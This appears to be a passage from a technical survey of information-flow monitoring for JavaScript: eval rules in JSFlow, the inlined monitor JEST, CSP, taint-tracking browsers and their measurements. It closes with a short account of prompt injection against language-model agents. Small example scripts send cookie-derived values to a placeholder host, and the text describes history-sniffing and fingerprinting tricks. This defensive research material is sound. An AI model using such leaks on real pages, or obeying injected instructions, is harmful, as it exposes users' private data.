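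These shares probably no longer hold, since `JSON.parse`, which reads JSON without running it as code, was still new in 2011. *What We Eval in the Shadows* (Goel, Donat-Bouillud and colleagues, 2021) examined 49 million calls to `eval` in R, a language for statistics. It found `eval` even more pervasive there than the earlier work had found it in JavaScript, but it does not update the figures for web pages.

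For information flow, the origin of a string run as code matters more than the number of calls. Richards and colleagues also tracked where each string came from, with separate categories for cookies and text the user had typed. In the manual browsing sessions, the largest group was strings that scripts had built from constants and simple values. Most of these strings would probably be public, so a monitor could run them like any other code on the page.

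### JSFlow's rule for eval

JSFlow runs generated code in a context at least as secret as the string it came from. For a call `eval(s)`, the rule by Hedin and colleagues has four steps:

1. Evaluate the argument to get the string and its label.
2. Parse the string into code.
3. Declare the code's variables in the nearest enclosing function, or globally if there is none, with the context pc ⊔ label(s).
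4. Run the code with the same context, pc ⊔ label(s).

If the string is public, the pc stays as it was. If the string depends on a secret, everything the new code writes depends on that secret too. In the following program, a secret chooses between two strings:

```
code = upg "l = 0;" to h;
if (h) {code = "l = 1;";}
eval(code);
```

The upgrade instruction gives `code` the label of `h`, so the assignment inside the branch can succeed. The call to `eval` is outside the branch, where the pc is low again, and neither string mentions `h`. If JSFlow ran the string with that low pc, `l` would end up with a low copy of `h`. The rule prevents this:

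| | h is false | h is true |
|---|---|---|
| String in `code` | `"l = 0;"`, high | `"l = 1;"`, high |
| Context of the new code | high | high |
| If `l` was low | stops | stops |
| If `l` was high | writes a high 0 | writes a high 1 |

When `l` is low, both runs stop at the same place, so stopping reveals nothing about `h`. JSFlow's rule for a function whose choice depends on a secret works the same way.

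A script can also put the secret into the text of the new code, as in `eval("l = " + h + ";")`. If `h` is 1, the string is `"l = 1;"`. Parsing turns the character 1 into a number literal, and JSFlow's core language gives every number literal a low label. The secret's label would be lost during parsing, so the rule first moves it from the string to the pc.

In the core language, `eval` is a statement without a result, but in full JavaScript it returns the value of the last expression in the string. A full interpreter has to add the string's label to the returned value, or `l = eval("" + h);` would leak the secret. The published rule covers only strings that parse. If the presence of a syntax error depends on a secret, the resulting exception reveals the secret, so an interpreter also has to check the string's label against the exception label.

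### A variable that exists only if the secret is true

Generated code can change which variable a later statement refers to. Hedin and colleagues give an example close to this one:

```
l = 1;
function f(x) {
  if (h) {eval("var l");}
  l = 0;
}
f();
```

The attack needs `eval` because it delays the declaration of `l` until the branch runs. An ordinary `var l` inside the branch would not work, because JavaScript declares all of a function's variables before running its body. If `h` is true, the function gets its own variable `l`, the assignment changes that variable, and the global `l` stays 1. If `h` is false, there is no local `l`, so the assignment sets the global one to 0. The global `l` therefore ends up as a copy of `h`, although the assignment is outside the branch and is the same in both runs.

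JSFlow represents the function's scope as an object with a structure label, so declaring a variable is the same as adding a property. The outcome depends on which labels the programmer has raised in advance:

| Labels raised beforehand | h is false | h is true |
|---|---|---|
| None | finishes, global `l` is a low 0 | stops at the declaration |
| Structure of the function's scope | stops at `l = 0` | finishes, global `l` is a low 1 |
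| Structure of the scope, and global `l` | finishes, global `l` is a high 0 | finishes, global `l` is a high 1 |

In the second row, JSFlow allows the declaration because the scope's structure is already secret. If `h` is false, the search for `l` passes through this scope without finding the variable, and its absence is secret. The write to the global `l` therefore happens in a secret context, and JSFlow stops it. In each of the first two rows, only one of the two runs can finish, which satisfies termination-insensitive noninterference. Both runs finish only if the programmer has raised both labels.

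In 2015, Chudnov and Naumann, in *Inlined Information Flow Monitoring for JavaScript*, described a variant that needs no second variable of the same name:

```
l = 1;
if (h) {eval("var x;");}
try {x;} catch (e) {l = 0;}
```

Reading a variable that does not exist throws an exception, so `l` becomes 0 only if `h` is false. Their own monitor is simpler and stricter than JSFlow, forbidding generated code from introducing new variables in a secret context even if a label was raised beforehand.

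### When two runs build different code

Secure multi-execution needs no label on the string, because each run executes the code that it has built itself. Suppose FlowFox treats the cookie as high, with an empty string as the default value:

```
code = document.cookie == "id=42" ? "n = 1;" : "n = 0;";
eval(code);
new Image().src = "http://host/?" + n;
```

If the cookie is `id=42`, the two runs execute different programs from the second line on:

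| Step | Low run | High run |
|---|---|---|
| Read the cookie | gets an empty string | gets `id=42` |
| Build the string | `"n = 0;"` | `"n = 1;"` |
| Run it | `n` is 0 | `n` is 1 |
| Request the image | sends 0 | skips the request |

The server receives 0 whatever the cookie is, and FlowFox does not have to understand what either string does.

However, default values are riskier in generated code. Suppose a page calculates a yearly income with `eval("yearly = " + income + " * 12;")`, and the low run gets an empty string for `income`. The generated code is then `yearly =  * 12;`, which is a syntax error. In an ordinary calculation such as `income * 12`, JavaScript would convert the empty string to 0 and continue. A policy writer who chooses the default without reading the script could not foresee this difference.

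Unlike code passed to `eval`, a script element becomes part of the page, and FlowFox keeps only one page for both runs. If the policy treats the insertion as low, the low run inserts the element, and the high run's version of the code never reaches the page. This is safe, but any feature that needs the secret in that code will fail. If the policy treats the insertion as high, the new element may contain a secret, so the browser must run its code only at the high level. Running it at both levels would pass any such secret to the low run through the page.

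The same situation can arise within a single run when the interpreter uses faceted values. If the argument of `eval` is `⟨k ? "n = 1;" : "n = 0;"⟩`, the interpreter has to run both strings, one with `k` in the pc and the other with "not k". Afterwards `n` is `⟨k ? 1 : 0⟩`, as it would be after an ordinary conditional.

### Staged analysis: leaving a hole for missing code

The methods above work entirely at run time. Jhala's 2010 talk, *Static, Staged and Dynamic Flow Analyses for JavaScript*, placed staged analysis between this approach and static analysis, which has to allow for every flow that could occur. *Staged Information Flow for JavaScript*, by Jhala, Chugh and their co-authors, treats code that arrives at run time as a hole in the program and uses residual checks to limit what may fill it.

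This short program illustrates the idea:

```
var c = document.cookie;
var copy = c;
eval(adCode);
location = next;
```

Suppose the advertisement's code in `adCode` must not obtain the cookie's value or influence where the page goes next. The analysis traces the cookie into `c` and `copy` and finds that `next` determines the new address. The residual check for the hole then only has to ensure that the new code does not read `document.cookie`, `c` or `copy` and does not write to `next` or `location`.

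The checks are syntactic, meaning they examine the text of the new code without running it, so *Staged Information Flow for JavaScript* could report almost no run-time overhead. If the new code has holes of its own, such as another call to `eval`, the system analyzes the code it has and produces further checks for whatever later fills those holes.

The tests used two policies of this kind, one for secret cookies and one for the address bar. Chudnov and Naumann report that these policies had a false-positive rate of 33% on the 100 most popular sites. They call this relatively low, but a site owner who enforced the policies would have to deal with many false alarms. They also report that the system did not support `with` or two common ways of calling functions, `call` and `apply`.

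The cookie policy also prevents the outside code from reading the secret at all, including any copies the page has made. A similar rule for selected text would disable the clipboard service on newspaper sites.

Code built from strings is difficult to analyse because a program can cut and join strings at any character. Lester, Ong and Schäfer, in *Information flow analysis for a dynamically typed language with staged metaprogramming*, study a language in which programs build new code from program fragments instead. Existing web pages would have to change before they could benefit from this approach.

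### Inlined monitors

An inlined monitor is a set of extra JavaScript statements inside the script it controls. A rewriter adds these statements before the script runs, and the browser executes the result with its ordinary engine, so nobody has to maintain a modified Firefox or WebKit. Site owners or users can place the rewriter on the server or in a proxy between the server and the browser.

The simplest design uses shadow variables. For each variable in the script, the rewriter adds a second variable that holds its label. In simplified form, `if (h) {l = 1;}` becomes:

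```
push(h_label);
if (h) {
  check(pc(), l_label);
  l = 1;
  l_label = pc();
}
pop();
```

The functions `push` and `pop` maintain a pc stack like JSFlow's, and `check` applies the no-sensitive-upgrade rule to the assignment.

A call to `eval` would escape all of this if the browser ran the string as it was, because the new code would contain no checks. The rewriter therefore has to process the string too:

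```
push(s_label);
eval(rewrite(s));
pop();
```

Magazinius, Russo and Sabelfeld were the first to point this out in print, according to Chudnov and Naumann. They proved the method sound for a small language with `eval` but without objects, functions or exceptions. Their automatic rewriter handled only a small part of JavaScript, and they transformed their test programs by hand. The added checks made these programs 20% to 1,700% slower, depending on the browser.

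Santos and Rezk later used shadow variables and shadow object properties in a rewriter for a subset of an older JavaScript standard. They proved that the rewriter enforces noninterference, and they extended the work to live collections in the DOM. But the subset leaves out exceptions, `for-in` loops, the operator `new` and automatic conversions, which account for many of the leaks that JSFlow has to close. They reported no speed measurements.

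### Boxes instead of shadow variables

Chudnov and Naumann wanted to cover nearly the whole language. Their system, JEST, supports the 2011 edition of the JavaScript standard outside strict mode, apart from the `with` statement. It replaces every value with a box, a small object with four fields for the value, its label, its type and some additional data. The rewriter then turns each operation into a function call on boxes. For example, `x + 1` becomes:

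```
xxopadd(x, xxprimlow(1))
```

The function `xxprimlow` puts the number 1 into a box with a public label. `xxopadd` adds the two values and combines their labels. If one of the boxes holds an object, `xxopadd` has to convert it itself, because the browser's conversion would call the script's `valueOf` and `toString` functions with unboxed values.

Function calls also preserve the program's meaning, because each argument is evaluated only once. If a simpler rewriter computed the label and the value of `y++ + x` in two separate expressions, both would run `y++`, and `y` would increase twice.

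Boxing every value adds a step to each access, but it means that the monitor's functions always receive the same type of argument, and a just-in-time compiler produces its fastest code for such functions. If only secret numbers had boxes, the functions would have to deal with many types. Chudnov and Naumann confirmed from the compilers' logs that, with every value boxed, the engine optimized these functions early.

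JEST builds a control-flow graph for each function to find where a secret branch ends, much as Bichhawat and colleagues do for bytecode. Exceptions can cross function boundaries, so JEST saves the pc stack at the start of a `try` statement and restores it in the `finally` block, however the statement ends.

### Protecting the monitor from the script

An inlined monitor and a malicious script run in the same language and share the same built-in functions. If the monitor relied on the page's own `toString`, for example, an attacker could change what the monitor does by replacing that function. JEST gives the script substitutes for the built-in functions, called facades, which work with boxes but never pass them to the browser. The facades also apply the policy wherever data can leave the page.

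The script must also be unable to read or change the monitor's variables. JEST keeps them out of the page's global object and starts each name with a random prefix, shown here as `xx`. A script could guess the prefix only by building names at run time and trying them with `eval`. The rewriter prevents this by refusing any generated code that refers to a monitor variable.

Code can also be spread across the page in script elements, handler attributes and URLs. Before rewriting, JEST collects all the code it can find into one script. This changes the behavior of some pages that use older HTML features that let a script affect how the browser reads the rest of the page. `document.write` fits this description, and in 2011 Richards and colleagues found it on 64% of the sites they used by hand.

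### The rewriter has to stay available

JEST's rewriter is a Haskell program, so it cannot run inside the page. When a script calls `eval`, the monitor sends the string to a proxy, which rewrites it and returns the result. The proxy must stay available while the page is open. Everyone who relies on the monitor must also trust the proxy, because the strings it receives can contain secrets. For example, `"l = " + h` includes the value of the secret variable `h`.

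JEST cannot yet handle `eval` if a site rewrites its scripts on its own server and visitors use no proxy. Chudnov and Naumann suggest compiling JEST, which is written in Haskell, to JavaScript and sending it with the page. JSFlow avoids the problem because its parser and interpreter are already in the browser.

### Four test pages and the measured slowdown

Chudnov and Naumann wrote four small web applications, each in an honest and a malicious version. One is a shop that shows a payment company's form in a frame. The shop must not receive the card details, and the payment company must not learn what the customer has ordered. Label sets such as JSFlow's can express both restrictions with one label for each company, neither above the other. The other three are a login service, a radio site with advertisements for concerts, and a currency converter that must not send the amount to its server.

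JEST stopped all the attacks, and the honest versions worked with two annotations. The payment page needed a declassification, because the payment company has to learn the total price even though the price depends on the secret order. The radio site needed an upgrade instruction. The applications were mock-ups, though, with only the code needed to show each pattern. Chudnov and Naumann had not tested JEST on live websites, and they considered it an open question how well the no-sensitive-upgrade rule suits existing web code.

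They measured speed with programs from SunSpider and Kraken, in an unmodified JavaScript engine with its compiler on:

| Program | Original | With JEST | Slowdown |
|---|---|---|---|
| Binary trees | 0.0027 s | 0.9267 s | 342× |
| Bit counting | 0.0043 s | 1.355 s | 315× |
| Fannkuch, a puzzle with permutations | 0.0532 s | 6.143 s | 116× |
| Partial sums | 0.0077 s | 0.7866 s | 101× |
| Reading JSON data | 0.0645 s | 0.5132 s | 8× |

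The reported overall slowdown with JEST ranges from 101 to 364 times, although the JSON program did much better, possibly because the engine's own JSON function does most of the processing. A faster mode reduced the slowdown for binary trees to 231 times by omitting the `with` statement that JEST normally wraps around the whole script, since most compilers cannot optimize code that uses `with`. That statement keeps global variables in sync with properties of the global object, so some scripts behave differently without it.

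The engine optimized the monitor's own functions but not the rewritten script. Chudnov and Naumann suspected that the large number of function calls was the reason. Rewriting turns an original loop with a comparison and a subtraction into a long chain of calls that each create or open boxes.

In a separate comparison that timed a single run of a program from start to finish, JEST was 15.6 times slower than the original and JSFlow 1,680 times slower. Inlining was therefore about a hundred times faster than a separate interpreter in this test. These times include starting the JavaScript engine, which takes the same time with or without a monitor. For a program that finishes in a few milliseconds, including this startup time makes the slowdown look much smaller than in the table.

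The Irvine group's figures make it doubtful that inlining could compete with modified engines, although Chudnov and Naumann saw some evidence that it could. The group's WebKit interpreter took about 6.3 times as long as compiled code on SunSpider, though with weaker tracking and on a different machine. Rewriting itself may cause part of JEST's slowdown. Caja, Google's rewriter for confining untrusted scripts, does not track information flow, yet it made programs 5 to 163 times slower in its mode for older scripts.

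The benchmarks do not include pages that generate much of their code. Chudnov and Naumann left out a benchmark based on real websites because it relies heavily on `eval`, which made reliable measurements difficult. On such pages, sending each string to the proxy would add a further delay to the slowdown shown in the table.

They did not expect any information-flow monitor to justify its slowdown for general browsing in the near future. They recommended inlined monitors for testing and security audits, where a long wait matters less, and for sensitive pages with little computation. To make JEST faster, they proposed rewriting only the parts of a script whose flows static analysis cannot determine. Generated code would complicate this, because a later `eval` could put a secret into a variable that the analysis had treated as public.

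### Why a hybrid monitor must analyze code as it arrives

A hybrid monitor raises labels by examining the branch that does not run, and that branch may contain code that does not exist yet. Suppose `fetchCode` stands for any function that gets a string from a server:

```
l = false;
if (h) {
  s = fetchCode();
  eval(s);
}
```

If `h` is false, the script never requests the string, so the monitor cannot determine whether running it would have changed `l`. The hybrid monitor of Hedin and colleagues leaves `l` public and falls back on the no-sensitive-upgrade rule, which stops the script if `h` is true and the string contains `l = true;`.

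The generated string may itself contain branches that depend on secret data. The monitor has to analyze these branches before they run, or it will stop harmless code as a purely dynamic monitor would. The browser therefore has to do the analysis each time a script generates code, and do it quickly, because a site owner cannot do it once and publish the results. Chudnov and Naumann chose the no-sensitive-upgrade rule without such an analysis for JEST, partly because they considered a sound and fast analysis of JavaScript very difficult, especially for code that uses `eval`.

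### Browser rules that forbid generated code

Current browsers let a site restrict generated code without tracking any data. Under the following Content Security Policy, a page may load script files only from its own origin:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self'
```

The same line also disables `eval`, the `Function` constructor and timers that are given code as a string. The browser refuses to run event-handler attributes and code written directly into script elements, including elements that a script inserts later. A site can permit the first group again with `'unsafe-eval'` and the second with `'unsafe-inline'`.

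Trusted Types, a newer browser feature, allows generated code under supervision. A site turns it on with another line in its policy:

```
require-trusted-types-for 'script'
```

Functions and properties that can turn text into code then reject ordinary strings and accept only special objects, which scripts must create with functions that the site has defined. One of these functions might allow script files only from a short list of addresses, and another might remove script elements from HTML. Developers can review these few functions instead of every place where the page handles text.

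Both rules mainly target attackers who inject text into a page and have the browser run it. They control which text may run as code but, unlike a monitor, they don't control where data may go, so a permitted script file can still leak a password. The policy above would also break a page that uses `eval` to read harmless JSON data from its own server, which a monitor would allow.

The restrictions could still simplify monitoring. If a page cannot generate code from strings, an inlined monitor no longer needs a rewriter for `eval`, and a hybrid monitor has fewer places where code is unknown until run time. Monitors must still handle code that arrives late, because a permitted script can insert elements that load more files from permitted addresses. JEST would need an exception to the policy above, since it runs its rewritten strings with `eval`.

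## Taint-tracking browsers: measuring leaks on the live web

A browser can also track data without enforcing any policy. It runs each page as usual, marks sensitive data with taint labels, and logs when marked data reaches a sink. Because it never stops a script, a false alarm wastes some of a researcher's time but does not break the page, and nobody has to add upgrade instructions. Most browsers of this kind ignore some or all implicit flows, which makes them simpler and faster. But they cannot guarantee that they catch every leak, because a script written to evade the tracking can send out a secret without appearing in the log.

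### One string from source to sink

The most precise taint trackers mark the individual characters of a string. Suppose the cookie in this script is `id=42`:

```
c = document.cookie;
id = c.slice(3);
url = "http://host/?u=" + id + "&p=home";
page = url.slice(-4);
new Image().src = url;
```

| Step | String | Marked characters |
|---|---|---|
| Read the cookie | `id=42` | all five |
| Cut out the number | `42` | both |
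| Build the address | `http://host/?u=42&p=home` | the 16th and 17th |
| Cut out the page name | `home` | none |
| Request the image | `http://host/?u=42&p=home` | the 16th and 17th, so the browser logs a flow from the cookie to the image address |

JSFlow gives a whole string one label, so if an address contains both the page name `home` and data from a secret cookie, it would treat `home` as secret too. A later request containing only the page name taken from that address would then cause a false alarm. Marking each character separately avoids this and shows the researcher which part of the address came from the cookie.

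The marks last only as long as the script copies the characters or computes with them. This loop rebuilds the number in another way:

```
copy = "";
for (i = 0; i < id.length; i++) {
  for (d = 0; d < 10; d++) {
    if (id[i] == d) {copy += d;}
  }
}
```

At the end, `copy` contains `42`, but both digits come from the public counter `d`. A browser that follows only explicit flows finds no marked characters in `copy` and logs nothing when the script sends it. To catch this loop, the browser must also mark whatever a script writes inside a branch that depends on marked data, as the best-known early systems did.

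### Early tracking in Netscape, Firefox and Chrome

Netscape 3.0, a late-1990s browser, already had a tainting module that attached one bit of taint to pieces of data. According to *An Empirical Study of Privacy-Violating Information Flows in JavaScript Web Applications* (Jang, Jhala and colleagues, 2010), Netscape abandoned the module in favor of signed scripts, partly because the module raised too many alerts.

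In 2007, Vogt and colleagues added taint tracking to Firefox by modifying the bytecode instructions of its JavaScript engine to keep a bit recording whether a value was sensitive. If a script sent a sensitive value to a domain other than the page's own, the browser reported a cross-site scripting attack, in which an attacker gets his own script to run in someone else's page. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues, 2019) lists the system among those that also track writes in branches that depend on secret values. A single bit cannot record which source a value came from, so it is better suited to enforcing one fixed rule than to surveying different leaks.

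Jang and colleagues wanted to survey several kinds of leak, so they let the researcher define the taint. Their modified Chrome reads policies such as this one, which looks for scripts that record clicks:

```
at $1.isClick() inject "secret"
at document.send($1, $2) block "secret" on $2
```

`$1` and `$2` stand for whatever objects or data occur at that point. The first line marks the result of the browser's own test for whether an event is a click. The second line checks the data in every network request for that mark.

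The browser passes each script through a rewriter just before the V8 engine runs it. The rewriter puts values into boxes that also hold their taint and the address of the script that created them. It resembles the inlined monitor JEST, but it is a C++ function inside the browser, so a script that calls `eval` does not have to wait for an outside proxy.

To track control dependence, the rewritten code keeps a stack like JSFlow's and adds every taint on the stack to the values the script writes. Likewise, the browser runs a click handler only if its test for a click succeeds, so anything the handler writes carries the taint of that test. Like the Irvine interpreter, the browser misses leaks through branches that do not run.

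Jang and colleagues measured the slowdown on the ten front pages with the most JavaScript among the 100 most popular sites. Scripts took 4.3 times as long on average with the first version and 3.0 times as long after optimization, which included rewriting two frequently used functions in C++. Whole pages took about 73% longer to load on a fast university network, where short download times make the extra work more noticeable. These figures include the overhead of tracking both copies and secret branches. That overhead is high for everyday browsing but was acceptable for the survey, which covered 50,000 front pages in about 50 hours.

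### Four kinds of privacy violation

Only one of the four searches covered all 50,000 sites:

| Violation | Front pages tested | Sites with reported flows | What manual checks found |
|---|---|---|---|
| Outside code obtains the page's cookie | 100 | 48, 38 or 17, depending on the policy | every flow was real |
| Outside code influences which page the browser opens | 100 | 0 | nothing to check |
| A script finds out which sites the user has visited and sends out the result | 50,000 | 63 | 46 confirmed |
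| A script sends out clicks, mouse movements or similar behavior | 1,300 | 328, or 115 after a filter | 7 of 10 tracked users covertly |

The cookie figures depend on what counts as an outside party. When host names had to match exactly, 48 sites leaked cookies. The number fell to 38 when all hosts within a domain counted as one party, and to 17 when any outside site used by at least three of the 100 sites was trusted. Even under the last rule, fbcdn.net counted as an outside party on Facebook's pages, although Facebook keeps most of its own scripts there. A real flow is therefore not always harmful, a problem the Irvine group also encountered.

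The third search was for history sniffing, the use of link colors to find out which sites a user has visited. One adult site among the 100 most popular checked whether users had visited 23 other sites. It stored their names with every letter shifted by one, decoded each name just before use, and added the site's number to a list if a link to it had the color for visited pages. It then put the list into an image address.

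The color only determines which numbers the script adds to that list and never enters the list itself, so a browser that followed only explicit flows would have missed the attack. Jang and colleagues were also lucky that their test browser had already visited all 50,000 sites in an earlier run, so the branches for visited links ran and left taint behind. With an empty history, the script would have sent an empty list and the browser would have reported nothing, even though an empty list also reveals something about the user.

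The other 17 reports may have been false alarms. In 12 cases the code was too complicated to understand, and in five the page contained a known sniffing widget that sent nothing suspicious during the test. Many of the 46 confirmed sites bought this service instead of writing their own code; 22 used code from interclick.com and 14 from meaningtool.com.

The true number of sniffing sites was probably higher than 46, because the browser did not follow data through the DOM or every built-in function. Another 422 sites read link styles, but the browser detected no transmission. Jang and colleagues considered 326 of these suspicious, often because a widget on the page checked a long list of outside sites.

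To study behavior tracking, they had a program call each page's event handlers as if a user were clicking, scrolling and copying text. The program also triggered the timers, because many scripts collect such data and send it only every few minutes. Most of the 328 reports involved something the user could notice, such as a larger picture that appears under the mouse. The group therefore discarded any request that drew a response of more than 100 bytes, assuming that a covert tracker's server would not need to send much back. This filter is rough, and three of the ten sites they then checked tracked visibly. The seven covert trackers included Microsoft's home page, which sent clicks and mouse movements to a statistics company. Seven more of the 115 sites used the clipboard service Tynt, and the browser detected copied text going to tynt.com on all of them.

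### Mystique: extensions and tracking cookies

For years, Chromium had taint tracking only for strings, which was enough to find some security holes but not to follow data through objects and numbers. *Privacy Implications of Emerging Web Technologies* (Chen, 2021) presents Mystique, a version of Chromium that tracks all types of JavaScript value. It was first used to study browser extensions, which can read the pages a user visits and, with the right permissions, the whole browsing history.

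V8 produces many different machine instructions for the same operation, depending on the types involved, and changing each of them to carry taint would have been a huge task. Mystique instead takes advantage of the fact that the engine always has the source code of what it runs:

1. It analyzes the source of a function and draws a graph of how data can move between its expressions, including dependence on branches.
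2. While the function runs, Mystique records which expressions have received marked values.
3. It passes the taint along the graph to the other values.

Mystique's prototype uses V8 with the optimizing compiler turned off. The slowdown would annoy someone browsing the web, but Chen intended Mystique as a service that checks extensions before people install them. A cluster of computers examined 178,893 Chrome extensions and 2,790 Opera extensions within a month. Mystique flagged 3,868 of them, or 2.13%, as potentially leaking private data. The ten most popular Chrome extensions with confirmed leaks had more than 60 million users combined.

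Taint tracking helps here because an extension can disguise the data it sends. Earlier researchers searched extensions' traffic for private data, which fails if the extension encrypts the data or uses its own encoding. Encryption is still a computation on the data, so the encrypted output remains tainted.

Chen later extended Mystique to track individual bytes in strings and used it to study cookies that third-party scripts set under the domain of the site the user is visiting. Trackers turned to these cookies as browsers began to block cookies from the trackers' own domains. Of the 10,000 most popular sites, 97.72% had such cookies. Of 26,632 different cookies, 4,212 could identify a user. Unlike the text search that Nikkhah Bahrami and colleagues used, taint tracking can recognize a cookie after a script has scrambled it.

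Mystique soon fell behind the browser it depended on. Xie, Kasi Murali and colleagues considered work of this generation unusable for a modern study because it relied on old browsers and old extension functions. They also objected that it mostly covered data about browsing, such as page addresses, rather than page contents. Their own taint tracker, Arcanum, covers both.

### Keeping up with the browser

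Mystique was built for Chromium 57. *PanoptiChrome* (Kanyal and Sarangi, 2024) reports that Chromium had since reached version 117, and that its developers had replaced the way V8 executes scripts and the way it manages memory. By then the browser had about 40 million lines of code, with another 3 million in V8.

PanoptiChrome combines a graph with run-time taint, as Mystique does, but keeps its changes in as few places as possible. All of its roughly 7,000 lines of changes are in V8's bytecode interpreter. Mystique changed the garbage collector, which frees unused memory, so that it would not delete the taint tables. PanoptiChrome protects its tables with a kind of reference that V8 already supports. Mystique also needed changes wherever the browser passes sensitive data to a script, and Chromium now has more than 7,000 such places. PanoptiChrome monitors these transfers from within V8 and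 reads its list of sources and sinks from a file, which researchers can edit without rebuilding the browser.

Kanyal and Sarangi used it to look for fingerprinting on the 20,000 most popular sites. They found 362 browser functions that scripts could use to recognize a user. Of these, 208 were previously unreported according to the paper's summary, but only 164 according to its introduction.

Project Foxhound, a modified version of Firefox, has more users. Its main purpose is to find places where a site's own scripts let an attacker's text run as code. The software company SAP and the University of Braunschweig maintain it jointly (Barber 2025, *ZAP Addon for Project Foxhound*). In November 2025, Barber was preparing an add-on that would let users of ZAP, a tool for testing website security, run Foxhound. Foxhound also works with Playwright, a program that operates browsers automatically.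 *Protecting Web Applications with Project Foxhound*, a 2024 talk, stresses that building taint tracking into a browser takes extremely high initial effort. A shared tool spares other researchers that effort.

*FP-tracer* (2024) extends Foxhound to mark numbers, so it can track details such as screen size, and measures fingerprinting on the 100,000 most popular sites. About 8% of domains showed high fingerprinting activity, and 75% showed at least moderate activity. In the most severe category, scripts disguised 46% of the details they sent, but the browser could still trace them. Consent banners gave no effective protection.

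In *Dynamic Security Analysis of JavaScript*, an independent comparison, Calzavara, Casarin and Focardi (2025) considered 18 systems for tracking information flow and got only eight to work. They wrote to the authors when download links were broken, and spent up to eight hours trying to run each tool they obtained. One of the eight, a version of JSFlow built into Chromium for fingerprinting research, failed to finish a single page within five minutes, a limit that allowed a slowdown of about 60 times. They could not configure another, which left six.

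The group then collected 110,533 different scripts from the home pages of 6,921 popular sites and counted how many each tool could process without a fatal error. For tools that failed on newer language features, they also tried converting the scripts to the JavaScript of 2009:

| Tool | How it tracks data | Scripts processed as they were | Scripts processed with conversion |
|---|---|---|---|
| Project Foxhound | modified Firefox | 95% | 95% |
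| JalangiTT | rewriting | 67% | 96% |
| PanoptiChrome | modified Chromium | 50% | 50% |
| LinvailTaint | rewriting | 47% | 63% |
| JEST | rewriting | 24% | 32% |
| IF-Transpiler | rewriting | 10% | 16% |

The four rewriters could not parse 31% of the scripts. They support only the old standard, and about a quarter of current scripts use newer features such as arrow functions. A rewriter is easier to install years later because it does not depend on a particular browser version, but someone has to update its parser as the language grows. A modified browser gets a current parser from the original browser, but PanoptiChrome still handled only half of the scripts, mainly because it stopped responding on complex websites. Calzavara and colleagues suspect that its developers missed this because they had operated it by hand and closed it after a fixed time.

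A tool can process a script without an error and still miss its leaks. On real sites, some of the tools detected no flows, the others disagreed substantially, and the slowdown could exceed 30 times. Calzavara and colleagues judged only Foxhound effective enough for large studies.

Keeping Foxhound current takes continued work because each Firefox release can change code that Foxhound has modified. Mozilla released Firefox 158.0 on October 13 (*158.0 Firefox Release*, 2026), and in November Brinkmann (2026) reported that a new stable version now came out every two weeks. A research tool can skip some releases, but a browser for the public would miss security fixes if it did.

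### Which kinds of flow matter in real programs

Staicu and colleagues tested how much a tracker misses by ignoring implicit flows. They collected 56 JavaScript programs with known security problems and wrote a policy for each. Most were for Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside the browser.

| Type of program | Number | Flow that the policy forbids | Are explicit flows enough to find the problem? |
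|---|---|---|---|
| Modules that let outsiders run code | 19 | outside input reaches a function that runs text as code | yes |
| Modules that an outsider can slow down | 20 | outside input reaches a slow text search | yes |
| Modules that expose old memory contents | 7 | uninitialized memory leaves the module or the server | yes |
| Browser scripts for fingerprinting and history sniffing | 10 | details of the browser or user reach a public output, such as an image address | not in general |

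The paper's text gives 19 for the second group, but its list has 20, which fits the total of 56. Tracking explicit flows was therefore enough for at least 46 of the programs, or 82%. Also tracking writes in executed branches that depend on secret data was enough for all 56, so none required a tracker to consider branches that do not run.

These results came from a single monitor that used the permissive-upgrade variant but continued where the original would stop. It counted each kind of flow separately. When a program used a partially leaked value, the monitor added an upgrade instruction at that point and reran the program, repeating this until no more were needed. This let it count flows from branches that had not run, which occurred in only five programs.

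Secret branches made tracking considerably more expensive. For the ten browser scripts, the group counted the operations in which the monitor had to handle a label or its stack:

| What the monitor tracks | Average number of operations |
|---|---|
| Explicit flows | 5,919 |
| Also writes in secret branches that run | 19,555 |
| Also secret branches that do not run | 20,890 |

The second row is 3.3 times the first, and the third adds 7% to the second. These are counts, not running times, so they suggest where the work is but don't predict the slowdown. They also leave out the programs that the strictest methods stop. The no-sensitive-upgrade rule would have raised an alarm at 5.46 times as many places in the code as the permissive variant, and most of the permissive variant's alarms were false too.

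Labels also spread further. The share of writes that stored a marked value was 45.4% smaller with explicit tracking than with tracking of secret branches that run. One module shows why this produces false alarms. In simplified form, it contains:

```
if (query instanceof Function) {
  part.operator = "$";
}
```

The query comes from outside, so the monitor marks the constant `"$"` as untrusted. If the module later passed that constant to `eval`, the monitor would report that an outsider could inject code, even though the outsider can decide only whether `eval` runs, not what it runs. When the policy is about secrets, the same pattern can be a real leak, because the attacker may want to know whether something happened. This probably explains much of the difference between the server modules and the browser scripts.

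### Scripts that try to hide a leak

The result for the 46 Node.js programs does not carry over to hostile code. As Staicu and colleagues point out, the programmers had made mistakes and were not trying to deceive anyone. Explicit tracking was insufficient for the ten potentially malicious browser scripts, even though nothing suggests that their programmers had a taint tracker in mind. Browsers often prevent a script from reading private data directly, so the script has to infer it from something indirect, such as the width of a piece of text, usually with an `if` statement.

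Tracking the branches that run would handle these scripts and also the digit-copying loop. But an attacker could get around it by running Hedin and colleagues' three-line program, which leaks through a branch that does not run, once for each bit of a secret. Staicu and colleagues expected attackers to turn to such methods if browsers introduced strong controls. They found no examples, but this is weak evidence about hostile scripts because they started from attacks that others had already discovered. In five of the ten browser scripts, they also never tried both outcomes of a branch that depended on a secret, so the tool may have missed flows there.

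Some attacks leave no data for a tracker to follow. Jang and colleagues describe a style sheet that gives visited links a larger font, so a script can detect a visited link by measuring how far an image below it has moved. In another attack, each visited link has its own background picture on the attacker's server, and the requests for these pictures reveal the user's history without any JavaScript.

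Such gaps matter less in a survey than in a defense. Few people browse with Foxhound, so most trackers gain nothing by evading it, and the disguises researchers have found so far, such as encoding and encryption, are explicit flows. If a popular browser began to block requests based on taint, companies that lost data would have a reason to rewrite their scripts, and could do it with something as simple as the loop with the counter `d`.

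## Interpreters for plans written by language-model agents

By 2024, researchers had begun to apply information-flow control to the plans that language models write for software agents, another kind of code that nobody can inspect in advance. An agent is a program that lets a language model use tools, such as functions that read a user's email or transfer money. In a prompt injection, an attacker puts instructions into text that the agent will read, such as a web page or an email. The model then follows these instructions as if the user had given them.

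In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed dividing the agent's work between two models. The privileged model receives the user's request and may use tools, but never receives text from outside. The quarantined model reads the outside text but has no tools. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's results by name, such as `$email-summary-1`.

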